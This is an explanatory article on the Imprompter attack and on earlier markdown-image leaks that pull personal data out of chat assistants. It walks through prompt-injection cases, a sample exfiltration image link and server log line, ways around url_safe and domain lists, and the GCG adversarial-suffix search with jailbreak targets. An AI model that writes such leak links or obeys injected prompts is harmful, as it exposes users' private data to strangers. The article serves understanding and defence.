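# Unreadable optimized prompts that make chat assistants leak personal data through image addresses

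## How a chat assistant's reply can send data to a stranger

*Imprompter* (Fu, Li and colleagues, 2024) describes an attack that steals personal data from a conversation with a chat assistant. A search algorithm generates prompts that look like gibberish to people but cause the assistant to pick names, phone numbers and similar details out of the chat and write them into an image address. When the chat page loads the image, it sends those details to the attacker's server. The attack worked on LeChat, the assistant of the French company Mistral, and on ChatGLM, a Chinese assistant. Mistral responded by blocking external images.

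The paper opens with an invented job applicant, Alice, who wants help with a cover letter. She finds a prompt on a site where people share them, pastes it into Mistral's LeChat along with her letter, and gets what looks like an empty reply. She decides the prompt doesn't work and tries another. By then a stranger has her name, phone number, address and email. Every piece of software involved did roughly what its makers built it to do, and nobody broke into Alice's computer or Mistral's.

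### Tokens and context

A language model processes text in short chunks called tokens. OpenAI's rule of thumb for English is that a token is about four characters, or three-quarters of a word. Capital letters and spaces matter, so "red", "Red" and "red" with a space in front of it can be three different tokens. Each model has a fixed vocabulary of tokens, and anything a user types, even if it isn't in any language, reaches the model as a sequence of tokens from that vocabulary.

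Given such a sequence, the model computes the probability that each token in the vocabulary comes next, usually written P(xₙ₊₁ | x₁, …, xₙ). After a formal letter ending in "Yours", "sincerely" gets a high probability, "truly" a lower one and "fridge" almost none. The software picks a token (either the most likely one or one at random according to the probabilities), appends it to the text and runs the model again, until it picks a special end token. The probability of a whole reply is the product of the probabilities of its tokens, each computed given all the tokens before it. So an attacker who wants a particular reply needs to find text that makes that reply probable.

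A model's context is everything it reads before it answers. According to *Context windows*, a page of Anthropic's developer documentation, this includes the system prompt (standing instructions from whoever runs the product), every message so far, documents and images, and the results of any tools the assistant has used. The largest current models take up to a million tokens, which Anthropic's *How context affects Claude's performance and cost* equates to about three copies of *Moby-Dick*. The user writes only part of the context. The product may insert notes from earlier conversations before the user's first message, and it resends the whole context on every turn.

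A prompt that Alice pastes in at the end of a chat therefore lands in the same sequence as her cover letter, and the model doesn't keep the two separate. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, contrasts this with databases. A database engine can keep a query apart from the data it handles, so programmers can stop an attacker's data from running as a command. A language model only predicts the next token, with no internal division between "instructions" and "data". Developers can train a model to favor some parts of its context, or mark which parts are data, but in his view these measures add a distinction that the underlying technology doesn't make.

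### The software around the model

A model on its own produces only text. A chat product adds a program that shows the conversation to the user and acts on certain patterns in the model's output.

One such pattern is the tool call, a piece of text in a fixed format that makes the surrounding software do something, such as open a web address or run some code. The format varies by vendor and may look like a line of Python, JSON (a common notation for structured data) or the tags of a web page. According to Fu and colleagues, the software scans the model's output as it appears. When it finds a tool call, it pauses the model, runs the tool with the values the model wrote, adds the result to the context and lets the model continue. The user normally doesn't see the code.

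The other pattern is the markdown image. Markdown is a simple notation for formatting text, such as using asterisks to produce bold type. An exclamation mark, a caption in square brackets and an address in round brackets together mean "show the image at this address". The part of the chat application that turns markdown into what the user sees is called the renderer. Vendors let it show images because people like charts and photographs in their answers. But the renderer will fetch an image from any address unless someone has built in a restriction. Fu and colleagues count image rendering as one more tool, which seems right, because here too the model's text makes one computer contact another.

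### One leak, step by step

Suppose a user named Dana Whitlock asks an assistant to improve a letter to her landlord. The letter contains her name, phone number and street address. She then pastes in a prompt that a stranger posted online with the promise that it improves any writing.

The product sends the model the full context, with the letter and the stranger's prompt both in it. The prompt makes one reply very probable, and the model writes it:

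`![a](https://example.com/Dana-Whitlock/555-0142/14-Elm-Street)`

The renderer recognizes a markdown image and converts it into the equivalent code for a web page. Dana's browser sees an image that it hasn't loaded yet and requests it. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, a security blogger's account of a 2023 leak from Microsoft's assistant, describes the same sequence and stresses that the browser connects without any click from the user. (Microsoft's fix let the page load images only from a few trusted domains.)

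A web address has two jobs here. The first part, example.com, determines which server gets the request. Everything after it is text for that server to interpret, and whoever composes the address can put anything there. The server at example.com belongs to the attacker, and like most web servers it keeps a log of requests. The log now has a new line:

`203.0.113.7 [12/Sep/2024:10:14:02] "GET /Dana-Whitlock/555-0142/14-Elm-Street" 200`

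The number at the start is the internet address of Dana's connection, which the attacker also gets. The rest of the line holds the time, the stolen details and a code for "request succeeded". The server doesn't need to have a file with that odd name, because the attacker gets the details when the request arrives, even if the server returns an error. In the Imprompter demonstration, the server returned an image of a single transparent pixel, so the reply looked blank.

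Marketers have long put invisible images into emails and web pages to learn who opens them. Those images reveal little more than the visit itself, because the sender fixes the address in advance. In the chat version, the model writes the address using whatever the victim has been discussing. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes the general danger that an assistant can give away private data through an address it loads in the background, even if no sensitive word appears in the visible chat. The image version can be called an image leak, though the programmer Simon Willison calls it "Markdown exfiltration".

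A tool call that opens web pages can send data out in the same way. Both methods require exact formatting. If the model leaves out a bracket or puts the markup in a code block, the renderer shows Dana a line of strange text containing her own phone number, and no data is sent.

### Prompt injection and jailbreaking

Prompt injection differs from jailbreaking in who the attacker is. In a prompt injection, the assistant follows an attacker's text while working for an innocent user, such as Dana, who only wanted a better letter. In a jailbreak, the user is the attacker and looks for wording that gets the model to ignore its maker's rules, for example to get the code for a phishing site.

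People often confuse jailbreaking with prompt injection, as Willison (2024) complained, and the terms have never quite settled. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, still used "prompt injection" for users' attacks on their own assistant. They introduced "indirect prompt injection" for attacks in which the attacker plants text where the assistant will later retrieve it, such as on a web page. OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes widely used lists of software security risks, treats jailbreaking as a subset of prompt injection, according to the trade outlet SC Media. Fu and colleagues distinguish the two by whether the user is innocent, which is more useful for identifying who gets hurt.

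The difference between a jailbreak and an image leak also affects which defenses can help. Companies train their models to refuse certain kinds of content, and a jailbreak has to overcome that training. An image leak doesn't, because a request to show an image breaks no content rule. A model that refuses every request for dangerous information could still write Dana's address into a link. Fu and colleagues point out that loading an image can be harmless or harmful depending on the task.

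The stranger's prompt reached Dana by a route that Greshake and colleagues also described. They called it "user-driven injection", in which the attacker gets the user to enter the malicious text. In one exploit they cite, the attacker secretly added a prompt to text that people copied from the attacker's website, and hoped they would paste it into ChatGPT without looking. The researchers expected that attackers could also persuade people to try prompts in a language they don't read.

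### Open weights, closed weights and gradients

A malicious prompt in plain English can fail if the victim reads it. When Willison summarized Imprompter in October 2024, he already knew about the image leak and identified the disguise as the new part. To find disguised prompts by computer, an attacker needs a kind of access that only some models allow.

A model's weights are the numbers, usually billions of them, that training sets and that determine the model's probabilities. The maker of an open-weight model publishes these numbers, so anyone with suitable hardware can run the model and inspect every step of its arithmetic. Mistral published the 12 billion weights of Mistral Nemo, and ChatGLM's developers published the 9 billion weights of GLM-4-9B. With a closed model, outsiders can only send text and read the text that comes back.

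Open weights let the attacker compute a gradient. The usual measure of how far a draft prompt is from producing a target reply, such as the line of image code above, is the loss. This is the negative logarithm of the probability that the model gives to the target reply, so a likely reply means a low loss. The gradient shows how the loss would respond to small changes in the input. Zou, Wang and colleagues (2023), in *Universal and Transferable Adversarial Attacks on Aligned Language Models*, used it to estimate how the loss would change if the token at each position in a prompt were replaced with any other token in the vocabulary.

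The gradient gives a rough score to every possible single-token swap at once. A prompt of 50 tokens and a vocabulary of 100,000 allow about five million such swaps, so running a large model on each one to improve the prompt by one token would be impractical. The scores are rough because a gradient describes tiny, smooth changes, whereas replacing one token with another is a jump. A searcher therefore uses the gradient to make a shortlist and runs the model on the shortlisted prompts to see which of them lower the loss. The procedure does not favor tokens that make sense to a human reader.

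Fu and colleagues did not have the weights of the models inside LeChat and ChatGLM. They assumed that each product ran a model close to its maker's open-weight release, computed their prompts on the release and then tried them on the product. Researchers say a prompt transfers when it was computed on one model and also works on another.

### Perplexity

"Gibberish" is a loose word, and researchers often put a number on it with perplexity, a measure of how surprising a text is to a language model. Hugging Face's *Perplexity of fixed-length models* defines it as the exponential of the average negative log probability per token. For a text of t tokens:

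perplexity = exp( −(1/t) × [log p(x₁) + log p(x₂) + … + log p(xₜ)] )

Here p(xᵢ) is the probability that the model gives to the i-th token after reading all the earlier ones. Take the phrase "Thank you for your help" and, for comparison, "Thank" followed by four unrelated fragments from different languages. With invented probabilities for the four tokens after "Thank", the sums go like this:

| Token after "Thank" | Ordinary phrase: probability | −log | Gibberish: probability | −log |
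|---|---|---|---|---|
| First | 0.8 | 0.22 | 0.001 | 6.91 |
| Second | 0.4 | 0.92 | 0.0001 | 9.21 |
| Third | 0.5 | 0.69 | 0.0005 | 7.60 |
| Fourth | 0.2 | 1.61 | 0.0002 | 8.52 |
| Average | | 0.86 | | 8.06 |
| Perplexity | | about 2.4 | | about 3,160 |

A perplexity of 2.4 means the model's predictions were, on average, about as uncertain as a choice between two or three equally likely tokens at each step. For the gibberish, the uncertainty was roughly that of a choice among three thousand. Perplexity depends on the model and on how it divides text into tokens, so scores from different models aren't directly comparable.

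Fu and colleagues scored their prompts with Llama 3.1 70B, an open-weight model from Meta. Ordinary prose scores below 10 on this model, while their optimized text prompts scored from about 1,900 to about 57,000. The plain-English instructions they wrote by hand for comparison scored between 110 and 616, well above ordinary prose, probably because they are short and full of address fragments and code symbols.

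## 2023 to mid-2024: plain-language prompts leak chats through images

The image leak predates Imprompter by about a year and a half. Two people found it in ChatGPT within days of each other in the spring of 2023, and both triggered it with instructions in ordinary English. By mid-2024 most large vendors had changed their products to stop it, though their fixes differed considerably and some were incomplete.

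### An instruction added to copied text

Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, found the leak at the end of March 2023 and described it in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*. When a visitor copies something from a web page, the page can run a small program that changes what ends up on the clipboard. Samoilenko's page used this to add an instruction for ChatGPT to whatever the visitor copied. He called this "copied prompt injection". It is a form of Greshake and colleagues' user-driven injection, since the user pastes the instruction into ChatGPT.

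The added instruction was for ChatGPT to put a markdown image in its answer and fill part of the image's address with something from the chat. The image was a single transparent pixel, as it later was in Imprompter. In one test, Samoilenko asked ChatGPT to fix a short piece of code, and his server received the corrected code with the image request.

A stronger version told ChatGPT to add such an image to every later answer in the chat, with the user's latest message in the address. Samoilenko then asked about the world's tallest building and the first president of the US, and both questions appeared in his server's log. A single paste could therefore expose what the user typed during the rest of the conversation.

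Samoilenko acknowledged that the attack was unreliable. ChatGPT's replies varied randomly, so a prompt that worked once could fail the next time. Success also depended on the chat's topic, where the instruction sat in the pasted text, and whether the user's next message was a question or a statement. When ChatGPT was slow, the user might notice the strange image code appearing. He gave no success rate, so his paper shows that the attack was possible but not how often it would have worked on real users.

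He also found that ChatGPT readily copied earlier messages and code into the address, but that it was very difficult to get passwords or API keys (the secret codes that programs use to log in to online services). He didn't explain why. His own demonstration did leak a password, though, because the instruction asked for "the code", and the code he had asked ChatGPT to fix contained one. Passwords and keys may have been hard to get because the instructions asked for them by name.

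Samoilenko agreed that users are responsible for what they paste and advised them to look it over quickly. But he thought the trick was too easy for users' caution to be enough, and he wanted OpenAI to stop ChatGPT from replying with markdown images at all.

### The same leak without pasting

Security researcher Johann Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, found the flaw in early April 2023. SecurityWeek, a trade outlet, credits the two men with discovering it independently. Rehberger's version mattered more in the long run because the victim didn't have to paste anything.

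OpenAI was then introducing plugins, add-ons that let ChatGPT do things such as read web pages and book flights. Rehberger's post *ChatGPT Plugins* (2023) describes an attack in which a user asks ChatGPT to read a page that contains instructions. ChatGPT follows them by summarizing the earlier conversation and writing the summary into an image address. In the demonstration, the stolen text included the phrase "TooManySecrets123", which the user had typed earlier in the chat. Greshake and colleagues had described this kind of attack, called indirect prompt injection, a few weeks before.

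A web address can't hold a long conversation because most browsers and servers limit addresses to around 2,000 characters (Wu, Zhang and colleagues, *A New Era in LLM Security*, 2024). Rehberger found a way around this too, which he described in *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* (September 2023). His instructions had ChatGPT use a second plugin to save the whole conversation as an online document or as a video with subtitles. The image address then needed to contain only the link to that document, and anyone with the link could open it.

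Rehberger told OpenAI about the image problem on April 9, 2023. OpenAI had no program for paying outside researchers who report flaws, so he and the company discussed it by email. OpenAI eventually told him that image rendering was a feature and that it planned no changes. When he sent the company a draft of his September post, he received only an automated reply.

OpenAI's position had some merit, since even Samoilenko had written that his attack didn't exploit any vulnerability. But the argument that users should check what they paste no longer applied once ChatGPT could fetch a web page by itself, because the model then read the attacker's text before the user had a chance to. Rehberger also warned against delay in *ChatGPT Custom Instructions*, because more and more plugins were using markdown images to display their results, and any later restriction would break some of them.

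### Domain lists, clicks and blocked images

Other companies accepted that they had a problem. Rehberger reported the leak to each of the vendors in this table and published the dates:

| Product | Reported | Fix confirmed | Time taken | Apparent fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat (Microsoft) | April 8, 2023 | June 15, 2023 | 10 weeks | Images load only from listed domains |
| ChatGPT (OpenAI) | April 9, 2023 | December 2023, web version only | 8 months | A server judges each image address |
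| Claude (Anthropic) | July 12, 2023 | July 26, 2023 | 2 weeks | An image loads only after a click |
| Bard (Google) | September 19, 2023 | October 19, 2023 | 1 month | A filter on data in image addresses |
| GitHub Copilot Chat | February 25, 2024 | June 12, 2024 | 15 weeks | Markdown images no longer displayed |

Some of these fixes probably came earlier than the table suggests. Google confirmed its fix only when Rehberger asked, and he later dated Microsoft's fix to May 2023.

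In Rehberger's test of Microsoft's Bing Chat, a comment or advertisement on a web page could take over the assistant while the user was reading that page. The assistant could then send out a summary of the conversation and any passwords elsewhere on the page. It behaved normally for a couple of turns before writing the image that leaked the data, so the user would have had trouble connecting the leak to the comment or advertisement.

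The part of Microsoft's fix that Rehberger could see was a content security policy. This is a set of rules that a website sends to the browser together with the page. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the official standard, describes it as a way for developers to control what a page can fetch or execute. The rule for images is called img-src, and MDN's *CSP* reference page gives its form: the name of the rule, followed by the permitted sources. Rehberger saw four permitted domains, all belonging to Bing, so the relevant line would have looked roughly like this:

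`Content-Security-Policy: img-src th.bing.com www.bing.com edgeservices.bing.com r.bing.com`

Suppose an attacker's comment gets Bing Chat to write an image address at example.com that ends with the user's secrets. The browser doesn't find example.com on its list of allowed sites, so it never sends the request and nothing reaches the attacker's log.

The defense acts after the model has followed the attacker's instructions. It doesn't depend on recognizing a malicious prompt, so it works equally well against plain English and gibberish. *EchoLeak* (2025), a paper on a later attack, recommends such policies because they prevent the user's software from making unintended requests.

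A list of allowed domains protects users only if attackers can't receive data at any of them. When Rehberger began testing Bard, Google's assistant at the time, with Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake, Google already had a content security policy that blocked their first attempt. But the policy allowed images from any address under google.com or googleusercontent.com, where anyone can host small programs through Google's Apps Script service. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* (2023) describes how Rehberger wrote one that copied the data in its web address into a Google Doc. When Bard's page loaded the "image" from that address, the program saved the chat in the attacker's document.

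The malicious instructions came in another Google Doc, which claimed to pass on a demand from the legal department. An attacker could share such a document without the victim's consent and wait for Bard to read it. Rehberger needed ten tries to get the wording right, and he had to include examples showing where the data should go, which other chatbots hadn't required. Google's fix left the policy unchanged, and images still appeared. He inferred that Google now filtered out addresses with chat data in them, but he didn't know how.

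Anthropic's fix let the user decide whether to load an image. Rehberger had uploaded a short biography of Albert Einstein to Claude, with an instruction inserted between two of its sentences, and Claude had put a summary of his earlier messages into an image address. After the fix, Claude's page showed a "Show Image" button and didn't load the image until the user clicked it. A user who clicks out of curiosity still sends the data. Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* (2023) calls the fix imperfect but says it prevents the automatic leak.

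The strictest option is to block all external images, as Mistral did after Imprompter. Attackers then have no list of allowed sites to search for gaps, but users lose charts and photographs from other sites. Clickable links can also carry data in their addresses. In January 2024, as Willison noted, Amazon similarly fixed a leak in its business assistant, Amazon Q, by preventing it from producing links.

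### ChatGPT's url_safe check

In December 2023, Rehberger demonstrated the leak live with a volunteer, who chatted with a custom version of ChatGPT that Rehberger had built to steal data. By the next day, OpenAI had changed the web version of ChatGPT. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes what Rehberger could work out about the change.

Before loading an image in a reply, the ChatGPT page now sent the image's address to an OpenAI server to be checked, using a function called url_safe. Rehberger tested this with an address on his own site that ended in an email address. The server returned `{"safe":false}`, the page left the image out, and his site received no request.

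Anyone can read the list of domains that a content security policy permits, but OpenAI kept its rules on its own server, so outsiders had to guess them from which addresses the server accepted or rejected. Rehberger wondered whether the server checked addresses against the index of Microsoft's Bing search engine, and hoped that OpenAI wasn't just using a language model to judge them.

He then tried to get around the check by splitting up the data. He used 36 image addresses, one for each letter and digit, and nine passed. The image for "a" loaded, for example, but the one for "d" did not, and he could see no reason for the difference. Using the addresses that passed, he sent the word "hi" to his server as two separate requests.

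None of these addresses contained private data. An address ending in "a.png" looks like that of any other small picture and is the same in every conversation. The information is carried by which pictures the model shows and in what order. If a server gets a request for "h" and then one for "i", its owner can tell that the model spelled "hi".

The leak is slow because a choice among nine pictures carries at most log₂ 9, or about 3.2 bits. A ten-digit phone number takes about 33 bits, so an attacker would need at least 11 image requests to send what used to fit easily into one. Rehberger went over the practical obstacles again in *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* (2026). Browsers cache images, so a repeated letter may not produce a second request, and requests can arrive in the wrong order. A long run of images is also easier to spot, both for the user and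 for OpenAI, which could check the records of its url_safe server. Rehberger suggested that OpenAI limit the number of images in a reply.

Wu and colleagues examined the check independently and published their results in February 2024. They used an ordinary browser's developer tools to watch the ChatGPT page request the check from the server. ChatGPT displayed an image if a prompt or web page spelled out its address in full, but the server rejected the address if the prompt told ChatGPT to replace part of it with a secret word. They concluded that the server approved any address that had already appeared in the conversation.

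That rule would be sensible, because the model can't have added anything to an address that somebody else wrote out in full before it replied. It doesn't obviously explain why Rehberger's "a" passed and his "d" failed, so there was probably more to the check. The check was weak because text from plugins also counted as part of the conversation, and ChatGPT could influence what a plugin returned. Wu and colleagues used this to get an address containing private data past the check, and their attack succeeded with all eight web-reading plugins they tried.

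The same researchers noticed that OpenAI had also tried to train or instruct the model not to write external image links. GPT-4 refused when a user asked for one directly, but complied when the request came from a web page or the link was part of a puzzle. Unlike a domain list enforced by the browser, the model's refusal depends on how the request is worded.

Another gap in the url_safe check was that only the web version of ChatGPT used it. The page in the user's browser requested the verdict, so OpenAI's programmers had to build the same step into every other app separately. The iPhone app didn't have it in December 2023. According to *Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024), the Mac app, which OpenAI released in 2024, didn't have it either. Rehberger would have preferred OpenAI to do the checking on its servers before sending the reply, which would have covered all the apps. He guessed that OpenAI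 wanted to display replies word by word without a delay.

Willison (2023), linking to *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, called the fix "half-baked". He found it strange that OpenAI hadn't simply blocked images from outside domains, and he expected attackers to hide data in file names or in the first part of the address. OpenAI didn't explain why it avoided simple domain lists until 2026, when it described a newer version of the check. It said that a trusted site may forward visitors to an untrusted one, and that strict lists produce so many warnings that people learn to click through them.

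Those drawbacks matter for a product meant to browse the whole web. But the 2023 evidence suggests that the domain list protects better against image leaks. Bing Chat's policy would have blocked all 36 of Rehberger's addresses, because none was on a Bing domain.

### GitHub Copilot Chat and a familiar flaw

GitHub Copilot Chat answers programmers' questions about their code. In February 2024, Rehberger showed that it would follow an instruction in a comment, a note in the code that the computer ignores when it runs the program. If a programmer downloaded a stranger's file and asked Copilot to explain it, names and codes from earlier in the chat could leak. GitHub confirmed the bug in March and said it was already tracking it.

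Accounts of the June fix differ slightly. Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat* (2024) reports that the assistant seemed to have stopped displaying markdown images, while Willison wrote in his note on *GitHub Copilot Chat* that GitHub had blocked only those from untrusted domains. GitHub switched off images in Copilot Chat completely in 2025, after Legit Security found another leak, described in its *CamoLeak*.

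By this time, the flaw probably surprised few people in the field. Willison was keeping a list of cases and had concluded that a chat interface is vulnerable if it handles private data, reads untrusted text and displays markdown images. At the end of 2024, Rehberger listed 11 affected products, five of them from Google. Each team that built a chat interface seems to have had to learn about the flaw separately. Google fixed it in Bard in October 2023, but its research assistant NotebookLM had the same problem the following April.

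### Stealing data with a list of addresses

In June 2024, Gregory Schwartzman of the Japan Advanced Institute of Science and Technology showed that an attacker could extract personal information from ChatGPT without using images. The attack in his paper, *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*, uses a tool call that opens web addresses. The victim pastes in a long piece of code with an instruction hidden in it. Schwartzman imagined an attacker luring people by promising that they wouldn't believe what ChatGPT produced from the code.

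OpenAI had anticipated the simplest form of this attack. ChatGPT would open an address that appeared in full in the prompt, but not one it had to complete with the user's age. Schwartzman got around this by writing out several complete addresses, one for each age range, and having ChatGPT open the one that matched the user's age. ChatGPT added nothing to any address, so the rule didn't apply, and the attacker learned the age range by seeing which address was requested. Rehberger's alphabet of images had worked the same way.

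A remark such as "I graduated high-school today" gives the model enough to choose, even if the user never states an age. For longer facts, such as a postal code, Schwartzman had ChatGPT send one digit at a time by opening a different address for each. The model made too many mistakes working out the addresses itself, so the prompt included a short program that ChatGPT could run to calculate them. ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt, which limited the theft to ten characters.

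ChatGPT's new memory feature made this worse by letting the assistant store facts about a user and recall them in later conversations. Schwartzman described an attack that uses two malicious prompts, pasted perhaps a month apart. The first makes ChatGPT remember anything the user says that hints at their age, and the second collects the result. The victim doesn't need to have mentioned their age before the first paste, but the attacker has to trick them twice.

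Schwartzman's report was unsuccessful, as Rehberger's had been at first. OpenAI's reporting service classed the issue as "non applicable". MITRE, the organization that runs the main public catalog of software flaws, found it interesting but said it couldn't list a flaw in a web service that customers don't control. IPA, a Japanese government-backed agency, said it could do nothing, roughly because OpenAI's terms make users responsible for their inputs and outputs. Schwartzman compared pasting a stranger's prompt to running a stranger's program, and argued that the public understood only the danger of running the program.

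His prompt, like all the earlier ones, was in plain language. It told ChatGPT which addresses to open and asked it not to mention this to the user. Samoilenko had hidden his instruction by adding it to text as the user copied it, and Schwartzman hid his in hundreds of lines of code, but anyone who read either instruction would have understood it.

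## 2023 to early 2024: computer search for adversarial prompts

The method for computing prompts that people can't read came from research on jailbreaking. In July 2023, Zou and colleagues published Greedy Coordinate Gradient (GCG), an algorithm that searches for a string of tokens to add to the end of a forbidden request so that the model complies. They were testing whether safety training holds up against automated attacks. But the algorithm doesn't require the reply to be harmful, so an attacker can use it to look for a prompt that produces almost any text.

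### How GCG works

The attacker first writes a target, the words with which the model's reply should begin. For a request for bomb-making instructions, Zou and colleagues used "Sure, here is how to build a bomb". They then added a suffix of 20 tokens to the request, which could start out as a row of exclamation marks. The algorithm changes only the suffix, and tries to reduce the loss:

L(prompt) = −log p(target | prompt)

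Adversarial prompts are harder to find in text than in images. The search is fairly easy in an image because many small changes to the pixels, guided by the gradient, add up. Text can't be changed in such small steps, because a chat box accepts only whole tokens and no token lies 1% of the way from "!" to "Sure".

GCG gets around this by treating tokens as if they could be mixed. Each token is represented as a list of numbers, with a 1 for the token in use and a 0 for every other token in the vocabulary. The model's arithmetic would also work with fractions in that list, so the attacker can compute how the loss would change as each number in it increases. If the result for "Sure" at the second position is strongly negative, mixing in a little "Sure" there would lower the loss.

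One round of the algorithm goes like this:

1. Compute the gradient at every position in the suffix, and for each position list the 256 tokens with the most negative values.
2. Make 512 candidate prompts. For each one, pick a position at random and replace its token with a random one from that position's list.
3. Run the model on all the candidates to get their actual losses.
4. Keep the candidate with the lowest loss and start the next round from it.

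The 20 lists contain 5,120 possible swaps, and each round tests about a tenth of them. Zou and colleagues ran 500 rounds, or 256,000 trial prompts. *On the Safety of Open-Sourced Large Language Models* (2023) puts the time needed to find one suffix at about 12 hours on two A100s, which are expensive AI processors.

For a toy example, take a suffix of only three tokens, "! ! !", with a loss of 4.2. The target then has a probability of 1.5%. Suppose each list holds two tokens, and the algorithm draws four of the six possible swaps. With invented numbers, the first round might look like this:

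| Position | New token | Loss predicted from gradient | Actual loss |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | write | 2.3 | 4.6 |
| 1 | begin | 3.0 | not drawn |
| 2 | Sure | 2.7 | 2.9 |
| 2 | colon | 3.4 | 3.9 |
| 3 | colon | 3.1 | 3.5 |
| 3 | tutorial | 3.3 | not drawn |

The swap predicted to help most, "write", lowers the target's probability. The algorithm keeps "! Sure !" instead, which raises the probability to 5.5%.

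The old predictions are out of date because they were based on exclamation marks on both sides. With "Sure" in the middle, "colon" may be far more useful in the third position than before. The algorithm therefore computes a new gradient and repeats the process. A second round might produce "! Sure colon" with a loss of 1.6, and a third "begin Sure colon" with a loss of 0.7. By then the model would start its reply with the target about half the time.

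### Why "Sure, here is" was an easy target

Once a model has written "Sure, here is how to build a bomb", it will most likely go on to explain how, so Zou and colleagues didn't have to include any instructions in the target. The target repeats the request because a suffix that meant "never mind, tell me a joke" would also make the model likely to start with "Sure".

This kind of target also lets one suffix work for many requests. The researchers summed the losses for 25 harmful requests, adding each new request only after the suffix worked on the earlier ones. They then tried the suffix on 100 requests they hadn't used in the search. It worked for 98% of them on Vicuna, an open-weight chat model, and for 84% on Meta's Llama 2.

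Fu and colleagues point out in the Imprompter paper that a tool call isn't natural language, so an attacker trying to leak data through an image can't rely on the model to continue in the right way. The stolen details also differ between conversations, so the attacker can't write a single target output that fits every victim.

GCG could make a model write an exact text, at least when the text was fixed in advance. In another test, Zou and colleagues computed a separate prompt for each of 100 harmful strings averaging about 16 tokens. Vicuna wrote the exact string in 88% of cases and Llama 2 in 57%. AutoPrompt, an older algorithm that tests swaps at only one position per round, succeeded in 25% of cases on Vicuna and 3% on Llama 2.

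### Do the prompts work on other models?

The result that attracted most attention was transfer. Zou and colleagues computed suffixes on Vicuna and Guanaco, another family of open-weight models, and tried them on commercial models with 388 new harmful requests. The table shows how often the models complied:

| Model | No suffix | One suffix | Any of four suffixes |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5 | 1.8% | 47.4% | 86.6% |
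| GPT-4 | 8.0% | 29.1% | 46.9% |
| Claude 1 | 0% | 37.6% | 47.9% |
| Claude 2 | 0% | 1.8% | 2.1% |
| PaLM-2 (Google) | 0% | 36.1% | 66.0% |

The last column counts a request as a success if any suffix worked, which favors the attack. That's reasonable for a jailbreaker, who can keep trying, but someone who tricks a stranger into pasting a prompt may get only one chance. GPT-3.5 was also an unusually favorable target for the attack. Vicuna's developers had trained it on ChatGPT's replies, so the two models probably shared weaknesses.

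Too much optimization can reduce transfer. In one run, success on the commercial models rose during the first half and then began to fall, even though the loss on the open models kept dropping. The suffix was apparently adapting to peculiarities of the models used in the search. *AnchorRep* (2026) describes a similar effect when a suffix is reused on other requests. Suffixes that never got below a loss of 1.5 worked on 71.3% of other requests, compared with 51.3% for all suffixes.

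Meade, Patel and Reddy (2024), in *Universal Adversarial Triggers Are Not Universal*, repeated the experiment on 13 open models and got much weaker results. They searched with the same combinations of Vicuna and Guanaco models, computed three suffixes for each combination, and counted only the improvement over the request alone. The average improvement was zero on Gemma 7B, Llama 2 7B and one version of Starling. Their developers had trained these models on judgments of which replies people prefer. Models trained only to imitate example replies were usually easier to attack.

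Suffixes computed on the 7-billion-weight version of Llama 2 failed on the 13-billion version, and vice versa. Meade and colleagues did reproduce the result for GPT-3.5, but they saw little transfer to GPT-4. They claim only that GCG doesn't reliably find transferable suffixes, not that such suffixes are impossible.

*Toward Understanding the Transferability of Adversarial Suffixes in Large Language Models* (2025) found that a suffix's success depended on the model, the request and the suffix itself. Suffixes computed on the better-protected Llama 3.2 transferred more easily to Qwen than the other way round. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) is the most relevant to data theft because it used GCG for prompt injection. Injections that had worked on a small Qwen model succeeded roughly 25–36% of the time on other Qwen models, less than 2% of the time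 on GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5, and at most 7.7% of the time on Gemini 2.5 Flash.

When a suffix computed on one model fails on another, the search method may be as much the cause as the target model. *Auditing Prompt Injection Defenses Before They Reach Users* (2025) tested two related Llama models, both trained to resist prompt injection. An ordinary GCG suffix computed on the first model never worked on the second. A stronger search, which also used intermediate versions saved during the first model's training, produced a suffix that worked on the second 63.9% of the time.

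So the 2023 figures don't reliably predict how well a GCG prompt will work on an unrelated company's model. Imprompter only needed prompts to transfer from a company's published model to the same company's product.

### Altered images that trigger tool calls

In *Misusing Tools in Large Language Models With Visual Adversarial Examples* (October 2023), Fu, Wang and colleagues tried to use an image to make a model misuse its tools. The group consisted of six of the seven people who later wrote the Imprompter paper and one other colleague. They could make small adjustments to the image's pixels, so they didn't need GCG's random swaps. In their scenario, the victim finds an attractive picture online and asks an assistant about it. The assistant answers normally but also writes a malicious tool call.

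The researchers adjusted the image's pixels to minimize the sum of the loss on the malicious tool call, the loss on the model's normal answer, and a penalty for visible changes to the image. Without the second term, the victim might get a strange answer and become suspicious. The researchers trained each image on many different questions because they couldn't know what the victim would ask.

They tested three pictures on LLaMA Adapter, an open-weight model that accepts images. An attempt had correct syntax if the software would run the call, and was exact if every detail matched the attacker's wishes. For questions about the pictures, the results ranged as follows:

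| What the tool call does | Correct syntax | Exact |
|---|---|---|
| Deletes all emails | 90–98% | 90–98% |
| Sends a short email | 92–100% | 92–100% |
| Sends an email containing a web link | 86–100% | 0–100% |
| Books a ticket | 0–46% | 0–44% |
| Loads a markdown image with the conversation in its address | 0–34% | 0–10% |

The abstract's figure of about 98% therefore describes the easy calls. For Samoilenko's image leak, in the last row, the best picture produced exactly the intended output in one case out of ten. Unlike the email calls, which were the same every time, the image address had to include the user's text, with spaces and punctuation converted into the codes that web addresses use. For questions unrelated to the picture, the exact rate was at most 8%.

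Even these numbers are the best of three attempts per picture. Runs that differed only in their random starting point could produce an almost perfect attack or a complete failure. Fu and colleagues argued that low success rates were acceptable because a picture that stays unnoticed can spread to many victims. That's only partly convincing, since a malformed call could reveal the attack.

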